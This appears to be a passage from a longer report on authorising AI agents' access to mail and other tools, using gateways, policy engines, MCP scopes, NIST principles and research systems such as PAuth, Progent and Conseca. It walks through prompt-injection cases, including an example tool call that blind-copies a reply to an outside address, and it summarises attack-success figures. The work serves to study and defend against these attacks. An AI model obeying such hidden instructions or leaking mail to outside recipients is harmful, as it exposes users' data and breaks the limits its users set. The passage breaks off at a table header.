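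Only the agent's program has Maya's whole conversation and a list of everything the agent has read. The rule for shared channels depends on that list. Ordinary code in the program can compare each tool call with Maya's rules and stop a misled model from emailing a stranger. But an attacker who controls the program can skip that code and send the token straight to Gmail. If the agent can run commands on Maya's laptop, it may also be able to skip the code by reading the token from the file that holds it and sending it to Gmail.

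Other companies also have to take these checks on trust. Meta launched a personal agent called Muse in September 2026. According to Digital Trends' *Amazon just kicked Meta’s AI shopper out of the digital mall*, Meta says Muse asks for confirmation before sensitive actions and that a monitoring agent, Sentinel, approves anything Muse sends online. A shop that receives an order from Muse cannot verify that either check took place.

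An MCP server receives the arguments of each call, so it can check an email's recipients, but it needs rules to check them against. In *Per-Tool OAuth Scopes for MCP, Derived from Your Schema*, Soormally describes an MCP server from the software company WunderGraph that at first let every connected agent use every tool, so a read-only analytics assistant had the same access as an administrator's agent. WunderGraph now uses the data fields each tool accesses to determine which scopes it needs. These checks cover only the server's own tools. If Maya's mail server refuses to send her messages to a stranger, the agent could still try pasting them into a web page.

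A gateway can apply one set of rules to many tools. An opinion article in Infosecurity Magazine argues that limits belong at a boundary the agent doesn't control, because nobody can hold an agent to account if it polices itself. A gateway works only if the agent has no other way to reach those tools. If Maya connected the agent directly to Gmail last month and nobody revoked its access token, the agent can bypass the gateway.

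Every request for Maya's mail has to go through Gmail, whichever program sends it. Gmail also has the messages and their arrival times. But it doesn't have her instruction or the information needed to determine whether a price in an outgoing email came from Acme's record or another customer's.

### One email through a gateway

Suppose the company's gateway holds a Gmail token for Maya with the scopes `gmail.readonly` and `gmail.send`. The agent holds only a token for the gateway, which Gmail would reject. On Thursday, a hidden instruction makes the agent add a blind copy to its reply to Ortiz:

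```
POST /mcp
Authorization: Bearer <token for the gateway>
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: send_email

to:      ortiz@acme.example
bcc:     audit@outside.example
subject: Your renewal
text:    The new term would start on 1 March ...
```

The body is simplified here. The gateway handles the request as follows:

1. It verifies the token, which names Maya, the agent and the task `acme-renewal-17`.
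2. It confirms from the company's records that the task is still open.
3. It reads the body and collects every recipient. The headers alone wouldn't reveal the blind copy.
4. It applies Maya's rules and refuses, because `audit@outside.example` is neither a known contact nor an Acme address.
5. The agent tries again without the blind copy. The rules allow this email, and the gateway counts it towards the limit of 20.
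6. The gateway builds a new email from the fields it has checked and submits it to Gmail with its own token.
7. Gmail checks that the gateway's token includes `gmail.send` and sends the email.

The gateway builds the email itself because Gmail's API accepts a message as a single encoded block, with the recipients inside. If the agent supplied the block, the gateway would have to read the recipients from it exactly as Gmail does, and any difference could let the agent email someone it isn't allowed to contact. The gateway should also reject line breaks in the subject, since the agent could use one to insert a Bcc line.

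To limit what the agent reads, the gateway can add Acme's addresses and the date 1 September to each of the agent's searches. It then checks every message Gmail returns before passing it to the agent.

The gateway's Gmail token is as broad as before. Someone who breaks into the gateway could use it to read all of Maya's mail and write to anyone. A mistake in the gateway's rules could expose the same mail without a break-in. If the gateway serves 500 employees, it holds 500 of these tokens, which makes it an attractive target.

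The company can reduce the risk by removing the Gmail token when the task ends. Auth0's *Intent, Not Just Permissions* describes Token Vault, a product that stores an agent's credentials and makes them inaccessible once the agent's task expires. In September, NIST (2026) finalised guidelines to help organisations avoid exposing tokens to attackers. These measures make theft less likely or limit how long a thief can use a token. Gmail would have to offer a narrower permission to limit what the token allows.

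### How does a policy engine decide?

In step 4, the gateway can consult a policy engine, which keeps the rules separate from the gateway's code. Cedar, an open-source language from Amazon, is one way to write those rules. Maya's rule for sending might look like this:

```
permit (
  principal == Agent::"renewal-agent",
  action == Action::"send_email",
  resource == Mailbox::"maya"
)
when {
  context.task == "acme-renewal-17" &&
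  context.now < datetime("2026-10-09T16:00:00Z") &&
  !context.has_attachment &&
  context.acme_people.containsAll(context.recipients)
};
```

The gateway sends Cedar the agent, the action, the mailbox and the context. Cedar returns "allow" if at least one `permit` rule matches and no `forbid` rule does. Otherwise it returns "deny". The order of the rules makes no difference, so Maya's rule can't override a `forbid` rule that the company adds.

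If a rule needs a fact that the gateway left out, Cedar skips that rule. Skipping is safe for a `permit` rule but not for a `forbid` rule. Suppose the company forbids attachments in a separate rule and Maya's rule doesn't mention them. If the gateway doesn't report whether an email has an attachment, Cedar skips the ban and may allow the email. The company can prevent this by declaring which facts every request must contain and having the gateway reject incomplete requests.

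Cedar has no "ask" result, but when it refuses a request, the gateway can test the request again as if Maya had approved it, and ask her only if the second result is "allow". Open Policy Agent, another widely used engine, can return any value its rules define, including "ask".

### Zanzibar and OpenFGA

Google's Zanzibar stores relationships between people and things and works out permissions by following them. If Maya belongs to the sales team, the sales team can view a folder, and a file is in that folder, then Maya can view the file. Google uses Zanzibar for sharing in Drive and permissions in YouTube, according to a personal blog post, *Scaling OpenClaw’s Agentic AI to Multi-User Environments with OpenFGA Authorization*. Cedar and Open Policy Agent mainly test conditions on the facts they receive, whereas a Zanzibar-style system stores the relationships itself. That suits questions such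 as "who can open Acme's record?", but a relationship alone can't express a deadline or a maximum number of emails.

OpenFGA is an open-source system based on Zanzibar that adds such conditions. In OpenFGA's *Modeling Task-Based Authorization for Agents*, an agent starts with no permissions, and the company's software grants each task only what it needs. Maya's task might have these grants:

| Holder | Relation | Object | Condition |
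|---|---|---|---|
| `task:acme-renewal-17` | `task` | `agent:renewal-agent` | None |
| `task:acme-renewal-17` | `can_call` | `tool_resource:read_record/account-4471` | Before Friday at 17:00 |
| `task:acme-renewal-17` | `can_call` | `tool_resource:send_email/ortiz` | Before Friday at 17:00, with fewer than 20 emails sent |

The top row binds the task to one agent. When the gateway checks with OpenFGA whether the task may email Ortiz, it also sends the calling agent's identity, and OpenFGA returns "no" if a different agent is using the task. The gateway has to authenticate the agent first, because OpenFGA relies on the identity it receives.

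The other rows name specific targets. A grant for `send_email` as a whole would cover every recipient. Each check covers one target, so the gateway must run a separate check for every address on an email.

OpenFGA's documentation shows one grant that lasts ten minutes and another that allows two calls. The caller supplies the current time and the number of calls so far. For Maya's limit of 20 emails, the gateway would therefore still need its own counter, protected against simultaneous requests as described earlier.

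If Maya's agent calls the price agent, it can share its task or create a new one with fewer permissions. A new task is safer because sharing would let the price agent email Ortiz. OpenFGA can also record a user's choice to "always allow" a tool, but that grant applies to all the agent's future tasks and brings back the standing permission this model is meant to avoid.

When the task ends, the company's software should delete the grants. Auth0 warns that the grants remain if the deletion fails, which is a good reason to also give every grant an expiry time.

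Small differences in the permission model can undo the separation between tasks. In Auth0's sample code, the check on a tool specifies the agent but not the task. If the agent is handling Acme's renewal and another customer's complaint at the same time, it could use tools granted for one task in the other. OpenFGA's version avoids this by checking the task's permission and then confirming that the right agent is using it.

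### What can an MCP server demand?

A Model Context Protocol (MCP) server can refuse a call when the agent's token lacks a required scope. The July 2026 MCP authorisation specification allows the server to work out the required scopes from the call's arguments, even if those scopes are not on its published list. Maya's mail server could accept an email to Ortiz but require a scope called `mail.send.external` for an email to a stranger.

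That is more flexible than a fixed scope for each tool, but the agent would still receive a named scope. If Maya granted `mail.send.external` so the agent could email one new recipient, it could also email any other outsider, unless the server also checked the address.

The server has to choose carefully when any of several scopes would be enough. In one of Soormally's examples, an agent needs one more scope, either `read:fact` or the broader `read:all`. WunderGraph's software compares options by the number of missing scopes, so it treats these two as equal and requests the first on its list. Here that is `read:fact`, but if the order were reversed, it would request `read:all`.

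Clients have also had trouble handling these demands. Soormally found that MCP's official TypeScript software kit replaced an agent's old scopes with the new ones. An agent that gained permission to write lost its permission to read, and when it requested read permission again, it lost permission to write, so the browser kept reopening for approval. Under the July specification, clients are supposed to combine the old and new scopes. In the February 2026 bug report *MCP step‑up consent not exposed for insufficient scope*, a user of the code editor Cursor described having to log out completely to grant a further scope.

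The MCP specification gives a server no way to demand that Maya sign in again. WorkOS's *MCP* (2026) gives the example of an agent that deletes a production database with a permission its user granted three hours earlier. The token is still valid, but the user may have left her desk. Another OAuth standard, RFC 9470, lets a server require a recent sign-in, but MCP hasn't adopted it. Asking for more scopes instead would be worse, because the agent would gain access while nobody was watching.

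MCP lets a server pause a call to ask the user for something, such as confirmation. Normally, the answer comes back through the agent's program, so an attacker who controls that program could answer for Maya. The server can instead send her to a web page outside the program, where the server must verify who she is. WorkOS recommends tying each approval to the user, the call's exact arguments and a recent sign-in, and letting the agent use it only once.

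The specification covers servers that agents reach over the web. If an MCP server runs on Maya's own computer and exchanges text with the agent directly, none of these requirements apply, and under MCP the server should take its credentials from the local environment.

*Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* (Tabata, 2026) concludes that the July changes clarify existing OAuth practice without adding fundamentally new ideas. MCP still has no standard way to write a rule such as "only people Maya already knows at Acme", so each server has to supply it.

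### What would a platform have to build?

To limit which messages an agent can read, Gmail would have to store Maya's filter with her grant and apply it to every way of reaching a message. Besides searching, an agent can open a message by its identifier, load a whole thread, download an attachment or connect through IMAP. If a thread contains replies from people outside the filter, Gmail would have to leave those replies out. Gmail should apply the filter before searching, because filtering the results afterwards can cause the leaks and missing results described earlier for Salesforce.

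Any Gmail server can check a scope on its own, but a limit on the number of emails needs a shared counter like the one described earlier. Google would have to decide what happens when that counter is unavailable. Refusing all mail would interrupt legitimate work, while ignoring the limit would let an agent exceed it.

The rules would have to keep their meaning for years. Suppose Google introduces a permission that limits recipients, and a year later lets users share a thread through a link. An agent with the old permission could use the link to reach anyone. Google would have to extend the old rule to cover links or block agents with that permission from using the new feature. It would also need a consent screen that Maya can understand and tools for administrators to test a rule before relying on it.

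### Why don't the platforms do this?

The permission documentation for Gmail, Microsoft 365, Salesforce and HubSpot doesn't explain why these limits are missing. Other companies and commentators offer several reasons, but these better explain why the limits are difficult to provide than why any particular company decided not to provide them.

*Authorization for Agents* (OpenFGA) says most credentials give agents broad access because the underlying authorisation systems don't support fine-grained permissions. It therefore advises companies to give an agent less access than an outside platform's credential allows, as the gateway does for Maya. If customers can set these limits themselves, the platform has less reason to rebuild its search and add counters.

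Agents that cross company boundaries also have no widely adopted standard. Infosecurity Magazine points out that each agent's developer has to build a separate arrangement for every platform. A platform that invented its own rules for recipients and deadlines would have to persuade developers to support them, and other platforms might not use the same rules.

The commercial reasons are clearest in online shopping. In September 2026, Amazon blocked Meta's Muse from its shop. *Amazon blocks Meta’s Muse AI assistant in new standoff over agentic shopping* (Bishop, 2026) reports that Amazon cited security, privacy and transparency, and describes the dispute as part of a fight over who controls the customer relationship. Amazon says in Engadget's *Amazon bars Meta's Muse AI from shopping on its site* that outside agents should respect a company's decision about whether to take part. Meta says Muse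 can use people's passwords without seeing them. Amazon has its own shopping agents, so it has a commercial interest in the outcome as well as a security concern.

Amazon requires agents to identify themselves with a line of text in each request. Muse doesn't send this line, and any program could copy it. To apply different limits to different agents, a platform first needs a reliable way to tell them apart.

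Google and Microsoft also sell assistants that compete with outside agents, and they might gain by reserving some features for their own assistants. But Gmail and Microsoft 365 already work with outside agents, and better limits could persuade more customers to connect them. The Amazon dispute shows that this motive can exist, but it isn't evidence that Google or Microsoft has acted on it.

### What does NIST propose?

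NIST began a project on agents' identities and permissions in February 2026 with a draft concept paper, *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*. In it, Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026) ask how a company can apply least privilege to an agent when nobody can fully predict what it will need to do, and how to judge the sensitivity of data that an agent has combined from several sources. The project would apply existing standards to agents, possibly including OAuth and MCP.

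Another candidate is Next Generation Access Control, a standard that represents users, data and rules as a connected graph and can change permissions in response to events. For Maya, the event could be Acme signing the renewal.

The project initially covers agents inside a company and excludes external agents from untrusted sources, such as Muse at Amazon. NIST received about 650 responses and later decided to include consumer uses, according to Biometric Update's *Traceable evidence will form the basis of AI agents*. In the same article, Ryan Galluzzo, who leads NIST's identity programme, said that standards are normally much more mature when such work begins. Respondents disagreed about whether to extend existing standards or start afresh, but more favoured extending them.

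NIST's August post *Back to the Future* (Fisher, 2026) warns against early habits such as sharing passwords with agents. Biometric Update's *NIST, European telcos converge on identity as foundation for agentic AI* quotes the post's criticism of static tokens, overly broad access and too many requests for human approval. A Japanese summary, @IT's *ヒューマン・イン・ザ・ループ万能説崩壊 NISTが提唱するAIエージェント運用のあるべき姿*, lists the technologies the post suggests for finer permissions, including Rich Authorization Requests and AuthZEN, a standard way for a gateway to consult a policy engine. With AuthZEN, Maya's company could replace its engine without rewriting the gateway. The post also describes a "flight plan", a set of actions that someone approves in advance so that the agent needs to ask less often.

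NIST published ten principles on 27 October in *Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems*, a post by Booth and three co-authors (2026). According to Biometric Update's *NIST sets 10 principles for AI agent identity and authorization*, they call for each agent to have its own identity, for access to be minimal, temporary and revocable, and for people to step in when the stakes rise. They also separate what an agent may do from what it decides to try, which favours checks outside the model. To stop a confused deputy, NIST recommends combining clear delegation, least privilege, separate policies and access decisions that always give the same answer to the same request.

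NIST acknowledges that current technology doesn't fully meet all ten. It plans demonstrations for companies and consumers, followed by a practice guide with working examples. The guide could help Maya's company build its gateway, but NIST can't require Gmail or Salesforce to offer narrower permissions.

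## Who decides the limits for each task?

The rules for Maya's task now cover senders, recipients, fields, dates and the number of emails, but she typed only two sentences. A person or a language model has to turn those sentences into rules before a gateway or platform can enforce them. The person could be her company's administrator or Maya herself.

The administrator can set limits that hold for every task but doesn't know what Maya needs this week. Maya does, but she won't write 20 rules to get it. A model can write the rules in seconds but may misunderstand what she wants. In tests, models have written such rules well when the task spells out every detail, but Maya's task doesn't.

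### Limits set by an administrator

*Intent-Governed Tool Authorization for AI Agents* (2026) treats the company's permissions as an upper limit that a user's request can narrow but never widen. If Maya's company forbids exports, her agent can't export anything, even if she tells it to.

An administrator could also write separate limits for each task. *Compromise Is Not Consequence* (2026) used this approach in its experiment, with a reviewed file that listed the permitted actions and resources for each task and that the model couldn't add to. That works for a fixed set of test tasks, but not for every task of every employee.

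Templates would reduce the work. The administrator could write one for customer renewals, with blanks for Maya to fill in the customer and deadline. The task grants described earlier suit this arrangement, and OpenFGA's *task based authorization* adds a separate check on whether Maya herself may use the record. But if Acme asks for a security questionnaire that only engineering holds, the template won't cover it, and someone has to decide whether the agent may fetch it.

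### Can users decide for themselves?

It is hard for a user to judge a request that arrives without its context. In the picnic example from Chen and colleagues, Alice's assistant asks on Tuesday for permission to book parks, without mentioning the picnic she requested on Monday.

Alice can only grant or deny the request. She might prefer to ask which park the assistant chose and whether there is a fee, but OAuth has no standard way to pause while she finds out. The task fails if she refuses, and Chen and colleagues say that agreeing feels like signing a blank cheque.

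They want requests to carry verifiable information about the task. The screen could then show "For the picnic you requested on Monday, book Sunnyvale Park on Saturday for $25." The authorisation server should take Monday's instruction from a signed record, and the park and price from the booking. If the agent wrote the explanation, a hidden instruction could make it write a misleading one.

There is little evidence on how people respond to such requests from agents. Sharma and colleagues don't measure how many users turn on automatic approval. Tsai and Bagdasarian (2025), in *Contextual Agent Security*, point to smartphones, where people may grant apps too much access just to use them. They expect permissions tailored to the task to cause far less confirmation fatigue, in which people who see many requests stop reading them, but they didn't test this with users. Chen and colleagues didn't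 test their example with users either, so it doesn't show how many people in Alice's position would click "Grant".

Sharma and colleagues assembled 100 typical tasks for agents, of which 44 need at least three tool calls and 26 need at least five. If the agent asked the user about every call, those tasks would produce at least 240 requests. Some would be about values the user never mentioned, such as a subtotal the agent needs for a later step.

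### How PAuth works out what a task allows

Sharma and colleagues designed PAuth (Precise Task-Scoped Implicit Authorization) to avoid these questions. The user signs the text of the task, and each server, without trusting the agent, works out which calls it should receive if the agent carries out the task faithfully.

Suppose a user asks her agent to check her Citi credit card balance and, if it is over $1,000, pay a quarter of it from her Chase bank account. Here is how PAuth would handle the payment:

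1. The agent's software sends the signed text to both banks, along with descriptions of the tools that each bank offers.
2. A language model at Chase translates the text into a short program, using a restricted form of the Python programming language. The model sees no emails, web pages or other outside data, so an attacker can't plant an instruction there for it to read.
3. Ordinary software finds the payment in that program and removes everything that doesn't affect it. Sharma and colleagues call the result a slice. In simplified form, it looks like this:

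```
let bal = Citi.getBalance("Me@Citi")
assert bal > 1000
Chase.transfer("Me@Chase", "Citi@Chase", bal / 4)
```

4. The agent asks Citi for the balance. Citi checks the request against its own slice and returns $1,200 in an envelope, a signed record of the value and where it came from.
5. The agent asks Chase to transfer $300 to Citi and attaches the envelope. Chase verifies Citi's signature, confirms that 1,200 is more than 1,000, and divides it by four. The amount and the recipient both match the slice, so Chase makes the payment without asking the user.

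If a hidden instruction makes the agent request $301, or send the $300 to someone called John, Chase asks the user about that specific payment. A permission for payments of up to $500 would have allowed both. The agent also can't get a larger payment through by claiming the balance is $4,000, because it would need Citi's signature on that figure.

Envelopes also work for longer calculations. In another of Sharma and colleagues' examples, one server returns 5, the agent adds 1, and a second server takes that 6 and returns 17. A third server accepts the value 134 because the task calls for 2 × 17 + 100, and the attached envelope proves where the 17 came from.

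If the model's program breaks the rules of the restricted language, the server lets the model try up to two more times. If those attempts also fail, the server authorises nothing for the task and asks the user about every call.

One drawback is that each server has to read the task. Maya's mail provider and CRM provider would both see her full instruction, even though each handles only part of the work.

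### What did the test of PAuth show?

Sharma and colleagues tested PAuth on AuthBench, which they built from AgentDojo. AgentDojo is a set of simulated banking, Slack, travel and office tasks for studying prompt injection. They added five shopping tasks to make 100. They also created 634 altered calls, which changed a value such as the amount or recipient, used a tool the task didn't need, or skipped a condition.

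PAuth accepted all 100 tasks without prompting the user and blocked all 634 altered calls. When a call is blocked, the server prompts the user for approval, so a user who approves every request would still let the altered calls through.

The researchers also had to reword some of the tasks to get this result. With the original wording, 71 tasks ran without a question and 29 didn't. One task originally asked the agent to invite a new colleague, Dora, to Slack and add her to the "necessary channels", but the details were in someone else's message. The new version gives her name, her email address and the two channels. PAuth treats any value that isn't in the task or in a server's data as unknown, and an unknown value never matches.

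The altered calls all differed from what the task required, so an exact comparison should block them whenever the slice is correct. The model produced a correct slice for every reworded task, which is the more informative result, and two of the researchers confirmed it by reading the slices. The researchers mainly used GPT-4.1, and three other models made no errors on the subsets they were tested on. With no failures in 100 tasks, the true failure rate on similar tasks could still be as high as about 3%. The translation cost between 0.2 and 3.8 cents per task, depending on the model, and each server has to pay for its own translations.

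PAuth's protection depends on three main assumptions:

- The task is unambiguous.
- The user reviews the text carefully before signing it.
- The server's model translates the text correctly.

PAuth also assumes that the user sees the real text on her screen, that connections are secure, and that a server reports its own data truthfully.

Even one of the published slices leaves some ambiguity. A user asks the agent to refund 10.00 that a friend has just sent. The slice searches the ten latest transactions for an incoming payment of 10.00 and allows a refund to its sender, but doesn't check that the sender is the friend. If two people had each sent 10.00, the refund could go to the wrong one.

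Sharma and colleagues argue that a faulty translation will usually lead to an extra question, because a wrong rule is unlikely to match an attacker's payment by chance. This is convincing for random errors, but less so when the rule leaves out a condition the user cared about, because other payments may then match it too.

PAuth also depends on the user's review. If a task refers to an address in a file, the agent can look up the address, add it to the text with highlighting, and ask the user to sign the new version. But PAuth is supposed to work even when the agent is compromised, and if the agent inserts an attacker's address, only the user can catch it. Checking one text is easier than checking a dozen calls, but a user tired of requests might sign it unread.

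PAuth doesn't suit Maya's task well. Its restricted language has no open-ended loops, and nobody knows how many questions Acme will ask by Friday. The agent's model also writes each reply, and PAuth treats text from a model as unknown, so the mail server would prompt Maya about every email. A looser slice could fix the recipients and leave the text unrestricted, but then PAuth would no longer check the whole operation.

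A company could still use PAuth for tasks like the credit card payment without waiting for every platform to adopt it. Sharma and colleagues suggest that a trusted proxy could check the agent's calls and then send ordinary OAuth requests, much as Maya's gateway does.

### Do Rich Authorization Requests mean confirming every step?

Sharma and colleagues argue that Rich Authorization Requests (RFC 9396) can't do the same job. They say each call would need its own permission with exact values, so the user would have to confirm every step.

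That is true if a platform's permissions accept only exact values. But Maya's mail permission in the earlier example covers up to 20 emails to known people at Acme, and she would approve it once.

The argument is stronger when a value depends on something the agent learns during the task. A platform could define a field for "a quarter of the Citi balance", but Chase would still need a trustworthy way to learn the balance. RFC 9396 doesn't provide one, but PAuth's envelopes do. A fixed limit would avoid a second question but wouldn't ensure that the amount is right.

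Someone also has to write the details in the request. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) gives the example of a user writing "triage these tickets", which expresses a goal but doesn't list the operations, recipients or time limit that a program could check. It concludes that the unsolved problem is turning the user's words into enforceable limits, not choosing a token format. The IETF's draft proposal *OAuth Mission* (2026) adds that an RFC 9396 entry expresses authority but not the task it serves. The proposal would make the approved task a separate object that a server can refer to when issuing tokens.

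### Progent: updating the rules during a task

PAuth fixes its rules at the start, but *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) lets a model write rules from the user's task and update them as the agent learns more. Each rule specifies a tool and conditions on its arguments, and ordinary software blocks any call that no rule allows.

In their example, a user asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice:

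1. The model reads the task and allows the agent only to search for that email.
2. The email asks for a summary of recent mail, to be posted on Slack. The model proposes new rules that let the agent read mail, look up the user's Slack name and post messages. These rules widen the agent's access, so they need approval.
3. The agent learns that the user's Slack name is `alice`. The model limits posts to that name. This narrows the agent's access, so the change takes effect automatically.
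4. One of the recent emails contains a hidden instruction to forward the whole inbox to a stranger. If the model is fooled and proposes a rule for sending email, that rule needs approval too.

Progent checks whether a change widens access with an SMT solver, a program that determines whether any values satisfy a set of logical conditions. The solver looks for a call that the new rules would allow and the old ones would block. The change goes through automatically only if no such call exists.

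So a misled model can't give the agent more access without the user noticing. But the solver can't determine whether a wider rule is a good idea. In steps 2 and 4, an email leads the model to propose more access, and the user has to recognise that Alice's request, unlike the stranger's, is part of the task.

Progent reduced the success rate of attacks from 39.9% to 1.0% on the AgentDojo benchmark and from 70.3% to 3.9% on the ASB benchmark. On both, the agent completed about as many tasks with Progent as without it.

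In these tests, every change was approved automatically to imitate a user who agrees to everything. The solver therefore blocked no changes, and the low figures show how well the model wrote and updated the rules. The initial rules alone reduced successful attacks in AgentDojo to 2.5%. Refusing every change that widened access was safer than approving them all. When a person reviewed the initial rules and each change that widened access, no attacks succeeded.

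Only 6% of the changes widened access and would have needed a person's approval. So few requests could limit confirmation fatigue, but the figure doesn't show how carefully an ordinary user would read them.

Progent also lets an administrator write fixed rules that take priority over the model's. The model can't allow a call that a fixed rule forbids, or restrict one that a fixed rule allows. If Maya's company has a fixed rule that lets every agent read mail, a rule from the model limiting this task to Acme's messages would have no effect. The company should therefore use fixed rules mainly to forbid calls, and allow a tool for every task only if it's harmless in all of them.

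Sharma and colleagues group Progent with systems that enforce the same prewritten rules for every task. This is true of Progent's fixed rules, but Progent also uses a model to write rules for each task.

Shi and colleagues acknowledge that Progent can't stop an attack that stays within the task's permissions. For example, text on a seller's web page could lead an agent to choose that seller's product from several valid options. Progent also doesn't check the agent's answers to the user.

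### Conseca: hiding untrusted text from the model

Tsai and Bagdasarian's system, Conseca, keeps untrusted text away from the model that writes the rules. The model receives the user's task, the tools' documentation and any information the agent's developer has decided to trust. In the prototype, this trusted information included email addresses, file and folder names, and the date, but not the contents of emails. The model writes a reason for each rule, and ordinary software enforces the rules.

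In one example, Alice asks her agent to answer urgent work emails. The model's rules let the agent send email as Alice to addresses at work.com, but only if the subject contains "urgent". They also forbid it from deleting anything.

The rule about the subject line is too narrow. If a colleague sends an urgent email with the subject "Server down", the agent will probably reply with "Re: Server down", and Conseca will block the reply.

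The rule about recipients is too broad. The model's reason for it is that the recipient must be on the list of work users, but the rule accepts any address at work.com. As printed, it would also match addresses that continue after "work.com", such as `eve@work.com.attacker.example`. If Alice read only the reason, she would think she was approving a stricter rule. Tsai and Bagdasarian rely on experts to confirm that the reasons match the rules, and suggest a simpler rule language for future versions.

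They tested Conseca on 20 office tasks, running each five times:

| Rules | Average tasks completed, out of 20 | Blocked inappropriate actions? |
|---|---|---|
| None | 14.0 | No |
| Fixed rules that block only deletion | 12.2 | No |
| Fixed rules that block all changes | 0.0 | Yes |
| Conseca | 12.0 | Yes |

The last column is based on a single planted email containing instructions to forward messages about security vulnerabilities to an employee. Without rules, the agent forwarded them even when the user had only asked it to sort her mail. Conseca blocked the forwarding in every task except one, in which the user asked the agent to carry out any requests in her urgent emails. The researchers wrote the tasks themselves and describe the results as preliminary.

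Conseca also blocked some harmless steps because the task didn't strictly require them. For example, it stopped the agent from creating an empty file before writing a summary, and the agent couldn't find another way to continue.

Conseca's model can't see the contents of emails, so it can't write good rules for a request such as "do what my manager's email asks". Progent can add rules after the agent opens the email, but then an attacker's email can also influence the rules it proposes. For Maya's task, though, a list of her known contacts at Acme would be enough for Conseca's model to write the rule about recipients.

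### Matching a task to scopes

It's simpler to have a model choose from the scopes a platform already offers. El Helou, Troiani and colleagues (2025), in *Delegated Authorization for Agents Constrained to Semantic Task-to-Scope Matching*, put the model in the authorisation server. A trusted proxy gives the server the user's original request, so the agent can't change it. When the agent asks for scopes, the server compares each one with the request and leaves out any that don't fit.

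Researchers have tried two methods for deciding whether a server should grant an agent the scope to use a tool. In the first, a model describes the ideal tool for the task, and software compares that description with those of all the available tools. The server grants the scope if the requested tool is the closest match and similar enough. In the second, the server prompts a model to judge whether the requested tool suits the task.

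To test them, they created a dataset called ASTRA from 12 real MCP servers with 10 to 90 tools each. It has 3,168 tasks, split equally between those that need one, two and three tools. It also includes unsuitable requests for other tools, some on the same server and some on different servers.

Outshift by Cisco's *ASTRA* reports that asking a model worked better than comparing descriptions on tasks with one tool, because the comparison often refused tools that the task needed. The researchers tested only the model on longer tasks, and it wrongly refused more tools as the number needed increased, especially when a task needed three.

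We would expect some of that increase from judging each tool separately. If a model accepts a necessary tool 90% of the time and its errors are independent, it will accept all three only 73% of the time (0.9³ ≈ 0.73).

*CAPMAS* (2026) predicts the whole set of permissions at once. Its best model chose exactly the right set for about 91% of requests, from 3,176 tools, in 17 milliseconds. For about one request in 11, the set had a permission missing or one too many. The list of tools is fixed during training, so adding new tools requires retraining, which took about 100 minutes for the full set.

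Even a perfect match wouldn't limit Maya's agent much. ASTRA's tool descriptions leave out the arguments, so the dataset tests whether an agent should be able to send email, but not to whom. With the narrowest scopes that Gmail or Microsoft 365 offers for her task, the agent could still write to anyone.

The right permissions can also depend on how the agent does the task. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) describes an agent that could prepare a report itself or send the records to an outside service for processing. The second plan needs an extra permission because the outside service sees the records. If the agent may choose any plan and receive whatever permissions that plan requires, it effectively chooses its own limits. Maya's instruction doesn't mention outside services, so the safer reading is that the agent may not use them.

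The same problem arises when one agent gives work to others. In a case study in *From Procedures to Permissions* (2026), a main agent assigned satellite images, survey data and a legal document to three specialist agents. After training, the main agent gave each specialist narrower access to tools and files, and they still completed the task. One example can't show how often training would have this result.

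### What does "Acme's questions" mean?

A person who knew Maya's work would probably understand her instruction. A model could interpret it in several reasonable ways:

| Maya's words | Too narrow | Too broad |
|---|---|---|
| "Acme's questions" | Only emails from Ortiz that contain a question mark | Anything that anyone using an Acme address asks |
| "about its renewal" | Only emails with "renewal" in the subject | Any email from Acme this week, including the invoice dispute |
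| "using the Acme record" | Only the renewal date and price | Every note and email linked to the record, including the lowest price Maya would accept |
| "answer" | Write a draft but don't send it | Agree to a discount |

If the rules are too narrow, Maya will probably find out. Suppose Ortiz writes, "Please send me the new contract length." The agent ignores the email because it has no question mark, and Ortiz complains the next day. That's annoying, but Maya can correct the rule.

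Maya may never notice that a rule is too broad. If the agent can read every note on Acme's record, nothing seems wrong until one of its replies mentions the lowest price she would accept. A model that is unsure should therefore choose the narrower rule, and the agent should ask Maya when it needs more access. But if the agent asks too often, she may start approving requests without reading them.

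It's better to settle the most important doubts before the agent starts. *Authenticated Delegation and Authorized AI Agents* (2025) proposes converting a user's instructions into structured permissions that people can review. The model could draft Maya's rules within the administrator's limits, and the company's software could show her a summary:

```
Until Friday 9 October at 17:00, your agent may:
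  read     mail from Ortiz and Acme Purchasing since 1 September
  look up  Acme's name, renewal date, renewal price
           and contract length
  write to Ortiz and Acme Purchasing

Please choose:
  Questions about invoices    [don't answer]   [answer]
  Requests for a discount     [don't answer]   [ask me]
```

The software should generate this summary from the rules. If the model wrote it separately, the summary might not match the rules, as in Conseca's example.

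The first choice changes which emails the agent may read, so the software needs a way to recognise them, such as Maya's renewal label. The second is harder to enforce because it depends on what the agent writes. If Ortiz asks for 10% off and the agent replies "Yes, that's fine", the recipient is allowed and the email contains no confidential data. The gateway could hold any reply that mentions a percentage or a price other than the one on Acme's record, but it would miss this reply because it mentions neither.

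## How much harm do narrower permissions prevent?

A hidden instruction harms Maya only if her agent chooses an action she didn't ask for and a server carries it out. A narrower permission can make the server refuse, but it doesn't affect the agent's choice. A test that counts only completed attacks can't separate the agent's choices from the server's refusals, because a low count might mean that the model ignored the instruction, that a permission blocked the request, or that the request happened to name a file that didn't exist.

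Tural Hagverdiyev measured the two events separately in *Compromise Is Not Consequence*, published in October 2026. After reading a hidden instruction, five small models carried out harmful actions in 8.9% to 37.8% of their decisions when they had a broad token, and in none when the token was limited to the task. The zero is weaker evidence than it appears, because the experiment counted only actions outside the task's permissions.

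### The same request under four kinds of permission

Language models vary from one run to the next. If a model tries to delete a file while a researcher is testing a broad token, and only reads the file while he is testing a narrow one, the narrow token looks safer than it is. Hagverdiyev avoided this by recording each request once and replaying it:

1. The model receives a task, such as summarising `report.txt`, and opens the file.
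2. The file contains an instruction to delete it. The model chooses its next action, and the test software records the request.
3. The software sends that identical request to the server four times, each time with a different kind of permission. It restores the files to the same state before each attempt.
4. If the server refuses, the model gets one more turn.

The broad token allowed any action on any resource. The other three permissions listed the actions and resources the task needed. One was an ordinary signed token, one was also tied to a key through DPoP, and one relied on Open Policy Agent to make the decision.

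The 128 scenarios covered files, calendars, mail and payments. The hidden instructions were to destroy data, disclose it, cause some effect outside the system or gain more authority. Each model ran every scenario ten times.

| Model | Valid decisions | Choices outside the task's permissions | Carried out with the broad token | Carried out with any narrow permission |
|---|---|---|---|---|
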